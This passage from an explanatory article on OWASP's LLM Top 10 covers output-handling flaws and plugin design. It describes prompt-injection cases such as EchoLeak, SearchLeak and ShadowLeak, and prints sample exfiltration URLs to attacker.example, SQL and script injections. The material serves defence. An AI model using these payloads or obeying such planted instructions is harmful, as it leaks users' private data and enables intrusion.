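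Web addresses cause a similar problem when the server fetches them, as in the earlier payroll example of server-side request forgery. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian built a concert website, TicketOracle, to measure how readily models carry out such attacks. Its assistant had one tool, which fetched any address the model supplied. An administrative service on the same machine accepted only local connections and could list and delete users. The researchers tried to make the assistant probe the machine for other services, read user records, delete data, and send a request to an address that returned no visible response.

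They tested seven models in April 2026, with ten attempts for each attack. Llama 3.3 70B made the forbidden request in all 40 attempts, GPT-5.2 and Claude Opus 4.6 made it in none, and the others fell in between. Gemini 3 Pro Preview refused to probe for services but carried out the deletion request every time. The exact rates should be read with some caution, because the ten attempts took place in a single conversation and earlier replies could affect later ones. Still, attacks on the same application could always succeed or always fail depending on the model.

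The researchers also added a list of permitted addresses to the system prompt, with an instruction to refuse all others. This blocked every direct attack. They then planted a concert review containing a false notice that the list now included the administrative service. When an ordinary user asked about reviews, Llama fetched the forbidden address in all ten attempts, compared with six of ten without the list. The other models never fetched it. The list itself may not have caused the increase, because the planted text in the test with the list included extra wording to get around it. Still, the result shows that a list in a prompt does not reliably stop a model from fetching other addresses.

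The same list would also have stopped Llama if it had been in the application's code. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian recommend that the model supply only an event identifier, from which the application builds the address. An application that must accept whole addresses should convert them to a standard form and reject those that point to its own machine or a private network. It should also check redirects, because a permitted site can redirect the server to a forbidden one. Network rules can add protection by blocking all outgoing connections except approved ones. Administrative services should require a login even for requests from the same machine.

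XML is a common format for structured documents, and some XML parsers will open a file or fetch an address that a document names. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian constructed a scenario in which an attacker persuades a model to include such a reference in a document it writes, though they did not cite a real case. Developers can prevent this attack by switching off the feature in the parser.

### What output schemas can and cannot check

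Many applications require the model's output to follow a schema, which specifies the fields the output must contain and the values each field accepts. A schema might require an order number with three letters and six digits, or a choice between "refund" and "exchange", and code can check exactly whether the output complies. A schema is most useful when the developer has already written the command and the model only fills in a few values, because a field that accepts only six digits can't contain a second command.

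Schema validation is much less useful when a field accepts free text. A request with one field called "query" can match its schema and still contain a command to delete every table. Validation checks only the structure of the request, so the database will still run the command.

Narrow fields can also contain harmful values. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian describe a public report from November 2025 about a shop's chatbot that looked up orders by number. The numbers followed a predictable pattern, so anyone could guess valid ones. The chatbot passed each number to the database without checking who owned the order, and returned other customers' email and delivery addresses. Every order number was well formed, but the lookup should have searched only the current customer's orders. Likewise, an internal address can be a valid web address, and a refund of 100 years' fees is a valid number.

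Software that parses structured output can itself have flaws. *Towards Demystifying and Repairing LLM-in-the-Loop Vulnerabilities* (2026) cites a 2025 advisory for remote code execution in vLLM, a program for running language models. The flaw was in the parser that extracts tool calls from the output of one model, Qwen3-Coder. Developers should therefore use a parser that never evaluates the data it reads.

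### How often researchers have found these flaws

The best direct evidence on SQL comes from tests of five open-source applications. For *Prompt-to-SQL Injections in LLM-Integrated Web Applications*, Pedro, Coimbra and colleagues (2025) hired a red team, a group of testers who act as attackers, and found that all five were vulnerable. *Words Become SQL* (Pedro, Coimbra and colleagues, 2025) breaks the results down by attack. Planted text could falsify answers in all five applications and change data in three, while direct requests could change data in four.

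One exception was an application that blocked write queries in its code, which prevented both kinds of attack on the data. Another ran only one query per question, so an attacker could not add an update after an ordinary search. GPT-4 generally took more effort to manipulate than GPT-3.5, but in one application it carried out a multi-step attack that failed with GPT-3.5.

The researchers also trained a small model on 361 malicious prompts from their manual tests and used it to attack the same applications automatically. It found 48 percent of the red team's attacks, so an automated scan that finds nothing is weak evidence that an application is safe.

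The clearest figure for code execution comes from an older study, reported in *A Survey on Large Language Model (LLM) Security and Privacy* (2023). Of the 51 applications tested, 16 were vulnerable to remote code execution and one to SQL injection. The study also found 13 vulnerabilities in six frameworks. These appear to be early results from LLMSmith, a tool that traces paths through a program's code from user input to dangerous functions and then tries to exploit them with prompts. According to Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian, the version published in 2024 reported 20 vulnerabilities in 11 frameworks.

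Neither study estimates how many applications in general are vulnerable. Pedro and colleagues looked for popular projects that connected models to databases, so their sample provides little evidence about applications that never run model-written queries. The models tested are also old. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian tried similar prompt-injection techniques on newer models without success, but they did not try to refine the prompts. Better resistance to manipulation would not help in OWASP's table-deletion scenario, where the user directly asks for the deletion and the model writes the query.

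*LLM-Enabled Open-Source Systems in the Wild* (Shifat, Baburaj and colleagues, 2026) examines 295 security advisories from January 2025 to January 2026 that mentioned language-model components. Code injection appeared in 24, path traversal in 18, SQL injection in 11, and two categories of command injection in 22 and 19, though one advisory can belong to several categories. Many of these flaws may have nothing to do with model output, since the researchers selected advisories by keyword and 35 of the advisories concerned software unrelated to language models.

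The advisories have no field for recording whether a model was involved, so the researchers judged this from the descriptions. After excluding unrelated software, two of them read a random sample of 100 advisories and matched them to OWASP's 2025 entries. They assigned 12 to Improper Output Handling, and 10 of those to Prompt Injection as well.

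## Model output displayed by browsers, chat clients and terminals

Browsers, chat clients and terminals act on some of the text they display, by running scripts, fetching images or applying formatting codes. An attacker who can influence a model's answer may therefore be able to run code in the reader's browser or get their private data.

### Scripts in the reader's browser

Web pages are written in HTML, which uses angle brackets to separate instructions from ordinary text. A browser treats anything between `<script>` and `</script>` as a program and runs it with the same access as the website's own code. In cross-site scripting, an attacker supplies that program, which may be able to read the page or send requests in the reader's name if the reader is logged in.

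In OWASP's scenario, a web application generates content from users' prompts, and an attacker writes a prompt that makes the model include a script in its reply. The script runs in a victim's browser, although OWASP does not explain how the reply gets there. It might appear in a product description or a shared conversation. The attacker could also plant the prompt in a review that the victim's assistant reads. OWASP attributes the attack to "insufficient validation of prompts", which is odd because the entry is about output.

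HTML encoding prevents the attack by replacing characters that have a special meaning in HTML with codes for displaying them. For example, it turns `<script>alert("Hello")</script>` into this:

`&lt;script&gt;alert(&quot;Hello&quot;)&lt;/script&gt;`

The reader sees the original characters, but the browser does not run them. This works in the body of a page, but other places need different checks. For instance, a link whose address starts with `javascript:` can run code when the reader clicks it, even if the address contains no angle brackets. The application therefore has to check the address's scheme.

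Chat clients usually display headings, tables and links. Models write these in Markdown, a shorthand that the client converts to HTML. If the client encoded this HTML, the reader would see raw tags. The client should instead use a sanitizer, which keeps harmless elements, such as paragraphs and bold text, and removes scripts.

A Content Security Policy adds a second layer of protection. The website sends the browser a list of approved sources, and the browser refuses to run scripts from anywhere else, including any that a faulty sanitizer let through.

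### Email templates

OWASP also describes an attacker who gets the model to put JavaScript into a marketing email. The script runs if the recipient's email program is vulnerable. Most email programs block scripts, so phishing is the more likely danger. A false link is more convincing in a message that comes from the company itself, and one manipulated template can reach every customer on a mailing list.

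The safest design is a fixed template in which the application encodes the model's text and supplies all the links. The application should also remove line breaks from the email's subject line. HTML has no effect there, but a line break may add headers to the message, such as extra recipients.

### Leaks through images and links

An image can leak data without any script. In Markdown, a model can include an image like this:

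`![Sales chart](https://example.com/chart.png?note=meeting-moved-to-friday)`

When the client displays the reply, the browser requests the image from example.com. The request includes everything after the question mark, so whoever runs example.com learns about the meeting, even if there is no chart at that address. Encoding the reply as HTML before converting the Markdown would not prevent this, because the line contains no angle brackets.

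An attack that uses this has six steps:

1. The attacker puts instructions in something the model will read, such as an email.
2. The user asks the assistant a question, and the application adds both the email and some private material to the prompt.
3. The model follows the instructions and writes an address on the attacker's server that contains some of the private material.
4. The client displays the address as a link or an image.
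5. The browser requests the address. It requests an image immediately, but it requests a link only if the user clicks.
6. The attacker reads the private material in the server's log.

Security researchers call the image version "zero-click" because the user does not have to click on anything the attacker supplied, though they still have to ask the assistant a question.

*Trust No AI* (2024) describes a version with a link in Microsoft 365 Copilot, Microsoft's assistant for office work. A phishing email made Copilot search the user's inbox and put what it found into a link in invisible characters. Clicking the link sent the data to the attacker. A researcher discovered the flaw in February 2024, and Microsoft fixed it that July. Amazon dealt with a similar leak in its business assistant, Amazon Q, by no longer displaying links.

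### EchoLeak in Microsoft 365 Copilot

In January 2025, Aim Labs, the research group of Aim Security, reported a zero-click leak in the same Microsoft product. *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Enabling Data Exfiltration* (Ravia, 2025) explains how the leak worked. Copilot answers employees' questions using their email, files and chat history. Outsiders cannot use it, but they can send an employee an email, which Copilot may later retrieve.

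The researchers wrote an email that covered many common workplace topics, so that Copilot would retrieve it for a wide range of questions. In the email, they told the model to put the most sensitive information available to it into a web address, and not to refer to the email, so the user would not see where the instructions came from. Microsoft's classifier for detecting injected instructions missed these because they appeared to address the human recipient and never mentioned AI.

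Copilot removed external links from its replies, but its filter missed Markdown links that put the address on a separate line from the link text. The attack still needed the user to click the link. The researchers avoided the click by using an image, but Copilot's Content Security Policy restricted where images could come from and blocked the request to their server.

The policy allowed images from SharePoint and Teams, two other Microsoft products. Both had services that fetched any address they received. The researchers put the address of their own server inside a request to one of these services. The browser allowed the request because it went to Microsoft, and Microsoft's server then forwarded the data to the researchers. The SharePoint version worked only if the user had accepted an invitation to the attacker's site, while the Teams version worked during ordinary use of Copilot.

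Microsoft rated the flaw 9.3 out of 10 (critical), according to the public record that GCVE (2025) reproduces. The US National Vulnerability Database rated it 7.5 (high). Both agreed that an attacker needed no account and no action from the user. Microsoft scored it higher because it judged that the effects could spread beyond the vulnerable component and that an attacker might be able to alter some data.

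Reddy and Gujral (2025), in *EchoLeak*, report that Microsoft fixed the flaw on its own servers in May 2025, with no action needed from customers, and published the details on 11 June. They add that Microsoft also began removing links in the overlooked form, along with embedded images, from incoming external content. SC Media's *Microsoft 365 Copilot ‘zero-click’ vulnerability enabled data exfiltration* reports Microsoft's statement that nobody had exploited the flaw in the wild. Reddy and Gujral's subtitle calls EchoLeak the first "real-world" exploit of its kind, but "real-world" refers to the product, since there were no known victims.

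The basic method was not new either. In *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Enabling Data Exfiltration*, a blog post with the same title as Ravia's, Willison notes that similar leaks had already appeared in "a dozen different products". He attributes them to a combination of private data, exposure to malicious text and a way to send data out. Copilot needs the private data to do its job, and many users want it to read outside email, so the way to send data out is often the easiest of the three to remove.

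### How an allowed site can defeat an allowlist

A Content Security Policy controls which sites the browser contacts, but it has no control over what those sites do next. If an allowed site fetches addresses on request, an attacker can use it to reach any other site:

`https://allowed.example/preview?url=https://attacker.example/private-data`

The browser permits a request to allowed.example. That server then contacts attacker.example, and the browser's policy does not apply to this second request.

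The same weakness reappeared in Copilot a year after EchoLeak. Varonis' *SearchLeak* (2026) describes an attack that began with a link to a genuine Microsoft address. When the user clicked the link, Copilot treated the search query in it as instructions. Copilot searched the user's email and put the subject line of a message, which sometimes contains a login code, into an image address. The image request went to Microsoft's Bing, whose image search then fetched the attacker's address.

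The list of allowed image sources that Ravia published in 2025 already included Bing, so fixing the Teams version of EchoLeak had not removed the underlying weakness. Microsoft has since patched SearchLeak too. The Hacker News' *One-Click Microsoft 365 Copilot Flaw Could Have Let Attackers Steal Emails, Files* (2026) reports that Microsoft rated the flaw critical, although its numerical score was only 6.5.

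Varonis recommends checking whether any allowed domain fetches URLs that users supply. This is difficult with a list as long as Copilot's, which covered dozens of domains and often all their subdomains. It is safer to allow images only from a server that stores the application's own images and forwards no requests.

If the application has to display outside images, Reddy and Gujral suggest a proxy, a server that fetches images for the browser, but only from addresses the application has digitally signed. This works as long as the application signs only addresses from sources it trusts. If it signs whatever the model writes, the proxy will forward data just as Bing did.

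Browser policies also cannot block requests sent from outside the browser. *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* (2026) describes ShadowLeak, an attack on ChatGPT's Deep Research agent when it had access to a user's Gmail account. An email contained hidden instructions for the agent to find sensitive data and visit a URL that included the data. The agent made the request from the provider's servers, so the user's browser could not block it and the user's company might have no record of it. ShadowLeak was reported in June 2025 and fixed in early August, with no evidence of a campaign against real users. Preventing this kind of leak requires limits on the agent's network access.

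### What each browser defence stops

The table shows what the main defences do when they work as intended.

| Defence | Script in the page | Image that the browser fetches automatically | Link that the user clicks |
|---|---|---|---|
| HTML encoding before Markdown conversion | Mostly stopped | Not stopped | Not stopped |
| Content Security Policy for scripts and images | Stopped | Stopped unless an allowed site forwards the request | Not stopped |
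| Removing links and images that point to unapproved domains | Not stopped | Stopped unless an allowed site forwards the request | Stopped unless an allowed site forwards the request |
| No automatic fetching | Not stopped | Stopped until the user chooses to load the image | Not stopped |

In its 2025 edition, OWASP recommended Content Security Policies only as protection against cross-site scripting. A policy written just for that purpose might not restrict images, and so would not prevent the zero-click leak.

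The client should filter links and images in each piece of a reply after converting it from Markdown to HTML and before adding it to the page. In EchoLeak, the filter examined the Markdown and missed one way of writing a link. All links have the same form in HTML, so they are easier to find there. SearchLeak succeeded because Copilot marked replies as plain text only once they were finished. It displayed each reply while the model was still writing it, and the browser requested the image before the reply was complete.

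Turning off automatic fetching is simpler and does not depend on an accurate list of safe sites. The client can show a placeholder and load the image only if the user asks. But users may get into the habit of loading every image. Showing the full address first helps, but few people would notice leaked data in a long address, and the 2024 Copilot attack used invisible characters.

Users need links to check sources, so removing all links would make many assistants less useful. Instead, the model can cite a document by number, and the application can insert the link from its own records. Because the model never writes an address, it cannot put private data in one.

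Reddy and Gujral also rate eight defences against the steps of EchoLeak, but they ran no experiments, so the ratings are only their expectations. For example, they expect a strict Content Security Policy to stop the attack, although Copilot already had a policy that restricted images. The strict policy would work only if it excluded every site that forwards requests.

### Additions in the 2026 edition

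OWASP broadened the entry in 2026. According to Invicti, it now explicitly covers clients that automatically fetch resources mentioned in model output, and terminals and code editors that act on ANSI escape sequences, which are control codes hidden in text. ReversingLabs reports the same additions but mistakenly lists them under another entry.

The 2025 edition already had a scenario in which a website summarizer sends private data to an attacker's server, but it did not mention automatic fetching. Developers who read only its description and list of common examples would have learned about scripts but not images.

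Respan (2026), a company that sells tools for testing AI agents, lists another addition: insecure code that coding assistants generate at scale. This also expands on the 2025 edition, which had a scenario about generated code that introduces vulnerabilities. It fits the entry less well than the other two additions because encoding or filtering can make text safe to display, but finding a security flaw in a working program usually requires review and testing.

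### Terminals and code editors

A terminal is a text window for typing commands and reading the results, and many coding assistants run in one. Terminals receive their formatting instructions in the same stream of characters as the text they display. An invisible "escape" character makes the terminal treat the next few characters as an instruction, for example to change the colour, move the cursor or clear the screen. MITRE warns that attackers can use these escape sequences to create fake prompts and, in some terminals, to run code.

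Embrace The Red's *Terminal DiLLMa* demonstrated the problem with a small program that sent a web page to GPT-4o and printed the summary. Instructions on the page made the model include escape sequences in its reply, and the terminal obeyed them. The effects included clearing the screen, which was mostly a nuisance, but other tests were more serious:

- In the terminal built into the code editor VS Code, the model's output created a clickable link that contained data from the prompt. VS Code asked the user for confirmation before opening it.
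- In the macOS Terminal, an escape sequence could make the computer look up a website's network address. If the website's name contained private data, the lookup sent that data to the attacker without a click.
- Escape sequences could put a command on the user's clipboard. Most of the terminals in the test removed the final line break, so a pasted command would not run until the user pressed Enter, but some did not.

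Some terminals have had similar flaws more recently. In *When Terminal Output Owns Your Clipboard*, Pelaseyed (2026) found that affected versions of the Warp terminal let escape sequences both read and change the clipboard without asking the user.

Escape sequences can also hide text from the user while leaving it visible to the model. Trail of Bits' *Deceiving users with ANSI terminal codes in MCP* (2025) tested this on version 0.2.76 of Claude Code, Anthropic's coding assistant. A malicious tool returned a description of the user's computer that included an instruction to download software from the attacker's server. An escape sequence made the instruction white, so it was invisible on a white background, but the model still read it and recommended that server. This method would fail on a dark background, but Trail of Bits also showed how to move the cursor and cover an instruction with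 a false report that a security scan had found nothing.

In these examples, the dangerous text came from a tool, not the model, so an application that cleaned only the model's replies would have missed it. Text from a tool can also alter requests for the user's approval. GCVE's *CWE-150* lists a flaw in OpenClaw, an AI agent, that let escape sequences in a tool's description change what the user saw in an approval prompt. Showing users the actual request protects them well only if the terminal displays it accurately.

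Trail of Bits recommends replacing every escape character with a visible placeholder before the text reaches the terminal. This disables escape sequences but leaves other control characters, such as backspaces, which can also hide text and which Embrace The Red included in its tests. A better approach is to make all control characters visible except ordinary line breaks and tabs. The application can add its own colours afterwards.

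## Insecure plugin design and how the 2025 edition divided it up

Most of the defences described so far are the responsibility of the application that passes on or displays a model's text. OWASP's 2023 list also had an entry for developers of the tools that models call, LLM07:2023, Insecure Plugin Design. It covered tools that accept loosely specified input and tools that assume every request comes from the user. OWASP dropped the entry from the 2025 edition. Some of its advice moved to Excessive Agency and some was already there, but OWASP left out the most specific parts.

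### Tools that accept too much

In version 1.1, OWASP gave three examples of bad input: a single text field for all parameters, a configuration string that can override a plugin's settings, and raw SQL or program code. Version 0.5 had also listed a complete web address. In each case, the model writes something the plugin's developer should have written.

OWASP's weather plugin shows the difference. Suppose the plugin tells the model to build a web address from a base address and the user's question, and the model sends this request:

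`get_weather(url="https://weather.example/forecast?city=Oslo&days=3")`

The plugin fetches the address and adds the response to the prompt. An attacker gets the model to send this instead:

`get_weather(url="https://attacker.example/forecast?city=Oslo&days=3")`

In version 0.5, OWASP described two consequences. The request reveals the plugin's network address, which helps the attacker look for other weaknesses. The attacker also controls the response, so the badly designed input allows prompt injection through a "forecast" that can contain instructions for the model, perhaps to call other plugins.

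A safer plugin accepts two separate values, or parameters:

`get_weather(city="Oslo", days=3)`

The developer puts the weather service's address in the plugin's code. The plugin checks that `days` is a whole number (a type check) and that it lies between, say, 1 and 7 (a range check). It also has to guard against a city value such as `Oslo&days=500`, which could add another setting to the address. It can look the name up in a list of cities, or encode it so that the ampersand counts as part of the name. The model may still supply the wrong city, but it can no longer choose the server.

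Fixing only part of a command is not enough. In another of OWASP's scenarios, a plugin adds a condition written by the model to a database query. Suppose the developer's part limits a search to the tickets of user 7, and the model supplies everything after the first `AND`:

`WHERE owner = 7 AND status = 'open' OR 1 = 1`

SQL evaluates `AND` before `OR`, so the condition holds for every row and the user sees everybody's tickets. If the plugin accepted only a status from a short list, the model could not add the second condition.

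OWASP said developers used free text to work around limits on context size, the amount of text a model can take in at once. Describing every parameter takes up some of that space. This matters less now that models accept much longer inputs. For tools that do need free text, OWASP recommended a second layer of code that parses the text into typed calls and checks them. Where that was impossible, it recommended inspecting the text for harmful operations, which is much less reliable, as the filters for generated code showed.

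### Requests that did not come from the user

Typed parameters do not help when the request itself is the problem. In one OWASP scenario, an attacker uses indirect prompt injection to make a code-management plugin transfer a user's repositories to someone else, which locks the user out. OWASP blames missing input validation as well as weak access control, but a request like this one would pass validation:

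`transfer_repository(id=812, new_owner="mallory")`

The number is valid and the account may well exist. Whether the plugin should make the transfer depends on who wanted it, and the request doesn't show who that was.

According to version 1.1, poor access control lets a plugin "blindly trust other plugins" and assume that the user supplied the input. OWASP also warned against authentication without explicit authorization for a particular plugin. Authentication only establishes who a user is, so logging in to a chat service does not authorize every plugin there to give away the user's code.

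In May 2023, the security blog Embrace The Red made the problem well known by showing that a web page could take over a ChatGPT session through plugins. The user asked ChatGPT to open the page with a browsing plugin. Instructions on the page then made the model use another plugin to read the user's email and send what it found to the attacker's server.

The blog called this cross-plugin request forgery, after cross-site request forgery. The model sends the unintended request instead of the browser, and the second plugin accepts it because it arrives through the user's own session. OWASP cited the demonstration under Permission Issues in version 0.5. OpenAI withdrew ChatGPT plugins in spring 2024, so this particular attack is no longer possible.

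Version 1.1 recommended OAuth2, a standard for giving an application limited access to an account. An OAuth token shows that the user once granted the plugin access, but not that the user wanted the current request. So OWASP also suggested authorization decisions that "reflect the plugin route rather than the default interactive user". Presumably, a request prompted by a web page would have fewer rights than one the user had typed. OWASP did not explain how a plugin could detect which route a request had taken.

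### The lowest-authorization rule

Version 0.5 had given more exact advice. Under Permission Issues, OWASP recommended taint tracing, which means labelling data from less trusted sources and tracking where it goes. A plugin would then run at the lowest authorization level of any plugin that had contributed to the prompt.

Suppose an assistant has three plugins. A web reader has level 1, because anyone can publish a web page. A company wiki that only employees can edit has level 2, and the user's mailbox has level 3. Each request runs at the lowest level among the plugins that have put text into the prompt, and a plugin rejects any request below its own level. The user's own words do not lower a request's level.

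| Plugin text in the prompt | Request | Level available | Level needed | Result |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| None | Send an email | 3 | 3 | Allowed |
| Wiki page | Edit the wiki | 2 | 2 | Allowed |
| Wiki page | Send an email | 2 | 3 | Refused |
| Web page | Read the mailbox | 1 | 3 | Refused |
| Web page and wiki page | Edit the wiki | 1 | 2 | Refused |
| Email | Open a web page | 3 | 1 | Allowed |

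The rule would have stopped the attack on ChatGPT. The page could still have made the model request the user's email, but the mail plugin would have rejected the request because the prompt contained text from a web page, even if nobody had recognised the page as malicious.

For the same reason, the rule blocks many legitimate requests. The assistant cannot find train times on a railway's website and email them to a user's colleague, or send a manager the main points of a wiki page. The application cannot reliably tell which parts of a prompt influenced the model's request, so it has to assume they all did. Once a web page enters the conversation, the level stays low until the application removes both the page and anything the model wrote after reading it.

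Asking the user to approve individual requests would restore some of this work, and the same OWASP list recommended manual authorization for sensitive plugins. But an assistant that reads web pages all day would ask constantly, and people who see many approval prompts tend to stop reading them.

The rule also misses some attacks. Suppose the user asks for a summary of their email and then asks the assistant to open a web page. The page contains an instruction to fetch a URL on the attacker's server, with text from the email included in the URL. Fetching a URL needs only level 1, so the web reader fetches it and the attacker receives the text. The rule only keeps untrusted text away from powerful tools, so preventing this attack would need a separate restriction on where data may go.

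A plugin's authorization is also a poor guide to whether its content can be trusted. The mailbox has the highest level because of what it can do, yet anyone can send the user an email. A hostile message would leave the level at 3 and could make the assistant send spam, which is one of OWASP's scenarios for Excessive Agency in version 0.5. Each plugin therefore needs two labels, one for what it can do and one for who can write the text it returns. If incoming email counted as level 1, the spam attack would fail, but the assistant could no longer answer messages without approval.

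Version 0.5 offered two blunter alternatives to taint tracing. An application could call only one plugin for each user message and clear the plugin's text before the next call, or it could block sensitive plugins after any other plugin had run. Both are easier to build but interfere with even more tasks. For example, looking something up in the wiki and emailing the answer would take at least two requests under the first rule and would be impossible under the second without starting over.

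OWASP kept the lowest-authorization rule when it merged Permission Issues into Insecure Plugin Design in July 2023, but had removed it by version 1.1 that October. OWASP gave no reason. A likely one is that the rule interfered with ordinary tasks, since much of the appeal of plugins was combining several tools in one request.

### How the entry left the list

OWASP started revising the list in early 2024 with a survey that drew more than 100 responses. In an interview that malware.news reposted, Wilson said that "everything is on the table", including the rankings and how the list classified vulnerabilities. The roadmap from OWASP (2024) set aside the second half of April for a vote on the existing entries. New proposals followed from mid-May to mid-June.

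The June newsletter from OWASP (2024) listed 34 candidates, with voting open until the end of the month. Three were rewrites of existing entries: Prompt Injection, Supply Chain Vulnerabilities and Overreliance. Nobody had proposed a rewrite of Insecure Plugin Design. Two candidates dealt with related subjects, but neither became an entry. Function Calling Attack was about models that let users run custom functions, and Unauthorized Access and Entitlement Violations was about systems that fail to enforce access controls.

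In July, OWASP (2024) planned to finish merging candidates by 1 August and publish on 1 October. By September the project was about four weeks late, and the OWASP (2024) newsletter reported 13 entries, two of them due for consolidation.

OWASP's working page *V2 (2024) New Entry Submissions* (2024) records the decision on plugins. As of 27 September, it listed a lead for each entry. The note next to Insecure Plugin Design was only "DEPRECATE (John S)". "John S" is probably John Sotiropoulos, who had written the 2023 proposal on insecure plugin integration. The page gives no reason for the removal and does not show whether he had recommended it or was only responsible for carrying it out.

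In October, OWASP (2024) asked members to choose ten entries from 12 candidates. Without Insecure Plugin Design, the working page has exactly 12 entries: eight existing ones, some already merged or renamed, and four new ones. The published list is those 12 minus two of the new ones, Backdoor Attacks and Insecure Design. So the plugin entry was almost certainly removed before the final ballot.

The newsletter that announced the ballot included a comparison from Wilson in which Insecure Plugin Design was "reemphasized" with more guidance on third-party risks. The editor joked that the comparison might be AI-generated. It does not match the published edition, though it may have described an earlier draft.

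On the working page, leads were asked to rename entries so that the names described vulnerabilities, and to avoid words such as "insecure". This is presumably why Insecure Output Handling became Improper Output Handling, although "improper" is not much more precise.

### The reasons OWASP gave

In its press release for the 2025 edition, OWASP explained why it had added Vector and Embedding Weaknesses and System Prompt Leakage, and why it had widened the old entry on denial of service. It also said that Excessive Agency "has been expanded" because new designs give models more autonomy, but it did not mention Insecure Plugin Design.

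Wilson didn't mention it either in Infosecurity Magazine's *OWASP Warns of Growing Data Exposure Risk from AI*. He said supply chain risks had risen from fifth place to third because they were mostly theoretical in 2023, but by 2024 there were real cases of poisoned models and tainted datasets. These problems come from components a developer obtains from others and have little to do with how the developer writes a tool.

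Sandy Dunn, a security executive who worked on the list, came closest to an explanation in early 2025. On the ITSPmagazine podcast episode *The 2025 OWASP Top 10 for LLMs*, she said the team had merged some entries and that insecure plugin design was "now included in supply chain". She described the changes as some reordering, "a little bit of clarity and combining". Neither she nor Rock Lambros, another contributor and the other guest, gave a reason for moving the entry.

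OWASP probably dropped the plugin entry partly to save space. Dunn said that members had debated a longer list, and that she had argued strongly for ten entries because twenty would overwhelm readers. OWASP had two new subjects to add, so it had to free two places. It freed one by merging Model Theft with denial of service to form Unbounded Consumption, and the other by dropping the plugin entry.

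Overlap with other entries is a weaker explanation, because Wilson did not see overlap as a fault. OWASP's November newsletter (2024) quotes him as saying he had "never been bothered" by it, since the list was meant to make people think about risks rather than sort them into exclusive categories.

### Where the advice went

Dunn's account fits only part of the entry. Version 1.1 stated that Insecure Plugin Design covered creating plugins and Supply Chain Vulnerabilities covered third-party ones. Installing someone else's plugin therefore already fell under the supply chain entry in 2023. However, that entry referred readers to the plugin entry for what to test before using a third-party plugin.

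Pillar Security's *Strengthening LLM Security* places some of the removed material under Excessive Agency instead. The text supports this placement better, at least for developers who write their own tools. The table compares the preventive advice in the plugin entry, the version 1.1 entry on Excessive Agency, and OWASP's *LLM06:2025 Excessive Agency*.

| Advice in Insecure Plugin Design, version 1.1 | Already in Excessive Agency, version 1.1 | In LLM06:2025 |
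|---|---|---|
| Separate parameters with type and range checks | No | No |
| Secure coding under OWASP's verification standard | No | Yes |
| Security testing during development | No | Yes |
| Minimal functions and access | Yes | Yes |
| User approval of sensitive actions | Yes | Yes |
| OAuth for access to a user's account | Yes | Yes |
| Authorization that reflects the plugin route | No | No |

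Only the advice on secure coding and testing clearly moved. The testing includes static analysis, which examines source code without running it, and dynamic analysis, which examines the running program. OWASP placed both under a general recommendation to follow good coding practice, with "a particularly strong focus on input sanitisation".

Excessive Agency already had two other controls in version 1.1, complete mediation and running each action under the user's identity, although they look as if they came from the plugin entry.

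The 2025 edition keeps only parts of the old requirement for typed parameters. LLM06:2025 advises developers to avoid open-ended extensions, such as one that fetches any address, in favour of narrower ones. It also criticises a tool that is meant to run one shell command but doesn't block others. LLM05:2025 requires parameterized queries for databases. A developer who follows all of this would probably avoid the raw SQL filter and the weather plugin that accepts any address. But neither entry says that a tool should take separate values and check the type and range of each, which was the first measure in the old entry and the easiest to apply. An instruction to sanitise input is weaker, because it suggests cleaning a free-form string instead of not accepting one.

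The 2025 edition handles authorization tracking less well. LLM06:2025 recognises that an earlier call to a malicious extension, or a compromised peer agent, can manipulate a model's output. It mainly recommends running each action with the user's identity and the fewest privileges necessary. But in the ChatGPT demonstration, the mail plugin was using the user's identity, which is why it released the email. Read-only access would not have helped, because the attacker only wanted to read the email. User approval might have worked, but LLM06:2025 provides no way for the mail tool to detect that a web page had prompted the request.

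Rich Harang, who worked on the 2023 list, gave the new edition a mixed review in his blog post *Thoughts on the 2025 OWASP Top 10 for LLMs release*. He wished he had tried to help correct its course, and he criticised several entries, but he praised the measures under Excessive Agency for requiring narrow tools, least privilege and checks against policy. He did not discuss the missing plugin entry. His summary of the new supply chain entry covers risks from software, models, data and licences but not plugins, which is another reason to doubt that much of the old plugin entry went there.

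Excessive Agency has been on the list since version 0.5 in July 2023, in eighth place until the 2025 edition moved it to sixth. Its expansion in that edition has led some writers to describe it as new. The Cyber Panel (2025) and NHI Mgmt Group's *OWASP Top 10 for LLMs shows identity gaps in agentic AI* both wrongly list it among the additions for 2025. The press release may have contributed to the mistake by describing the expansion alongside two entries that were new.

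### From "plugin" to "extension"

The 2025 edition also replaced the term "plugins" with "extensions". LLM06:2025 notes that vendors may call them tools, skills or plugins. OWASP did not explain this change either. "Plugin" had become closely associated with a ChatGPT feature that no longer existed, and other companies used different names for much the same thing.

The editors missed some old terms in LLM06:2025. The entry still refers to "an LLM plugin with open-ended functionality", and to an abandoned but still available extension as the "original plugin". It also uses the name Insecure Output Handling for an entry that the same edition renamed.

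OWASP could have kept the entry and renamed it Insecure Extension Design, so the new vocabulary does not explain the removal. Tools had become more common in the meantime, and the press release cited the growth of agents as a reason to expand Excessive Agency.

### The same faults in the Model Context Protocol

Many applications connect models to tools through MCP. An MCP server describes each tool to the application, including a schema for its input. The schema makes the 2023 advice on typed parameters easier to follow, but a developer can still define a single free-text field instead of narrow parameters.

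In 2025, Snyk Labs attacked an MCP server for Amazon's cloud that had both of the old faults. Its tool accepted a whole command as text. A narrower tool for listing storage folders could have accepted only a region from a fixed list, which would have prevented the attacker from submitting a command.

The server also could not distinguish the developer's request from the command planted in a shared file. The two arrived together, and the server carried out both with whatever access it had on the developer's machine. An OAuth login would not have separated them, because the developer's own assistant sent both.

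The lowest-authorization rule would have missed this attack if applied literally, because the rule counts text from plugins and the developer had added the file directly to the assistant's context. An application would have to label text by who could have written it, however it arrived. Tool descriptions need this label too, because they also go into the prompt. A malicious server can use them to influence requests to other servers before the model has called any of the malicious server's tools.

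With those labels, the rule would block the command, but it would also make a coding assistant nearly useless, because such assistants spend most of their time reading files other people wrote and then running commands. A workable version would have to let low-trust text lead to harmless actions, such as running tests in an isolated environment without network access, and require approval for anything that touches the developer's cloud account.

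OWASP now has a separate guide for people who write these servers, *A Practical Guide for Secure MCP Server Development*, which it lists on its download page for the 2025 edition. The 2026 Top 10, as reported by SC Media, still has no entry on the design of plugins, extensions or tools.

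## Excessive functionality, permissions and autonomy

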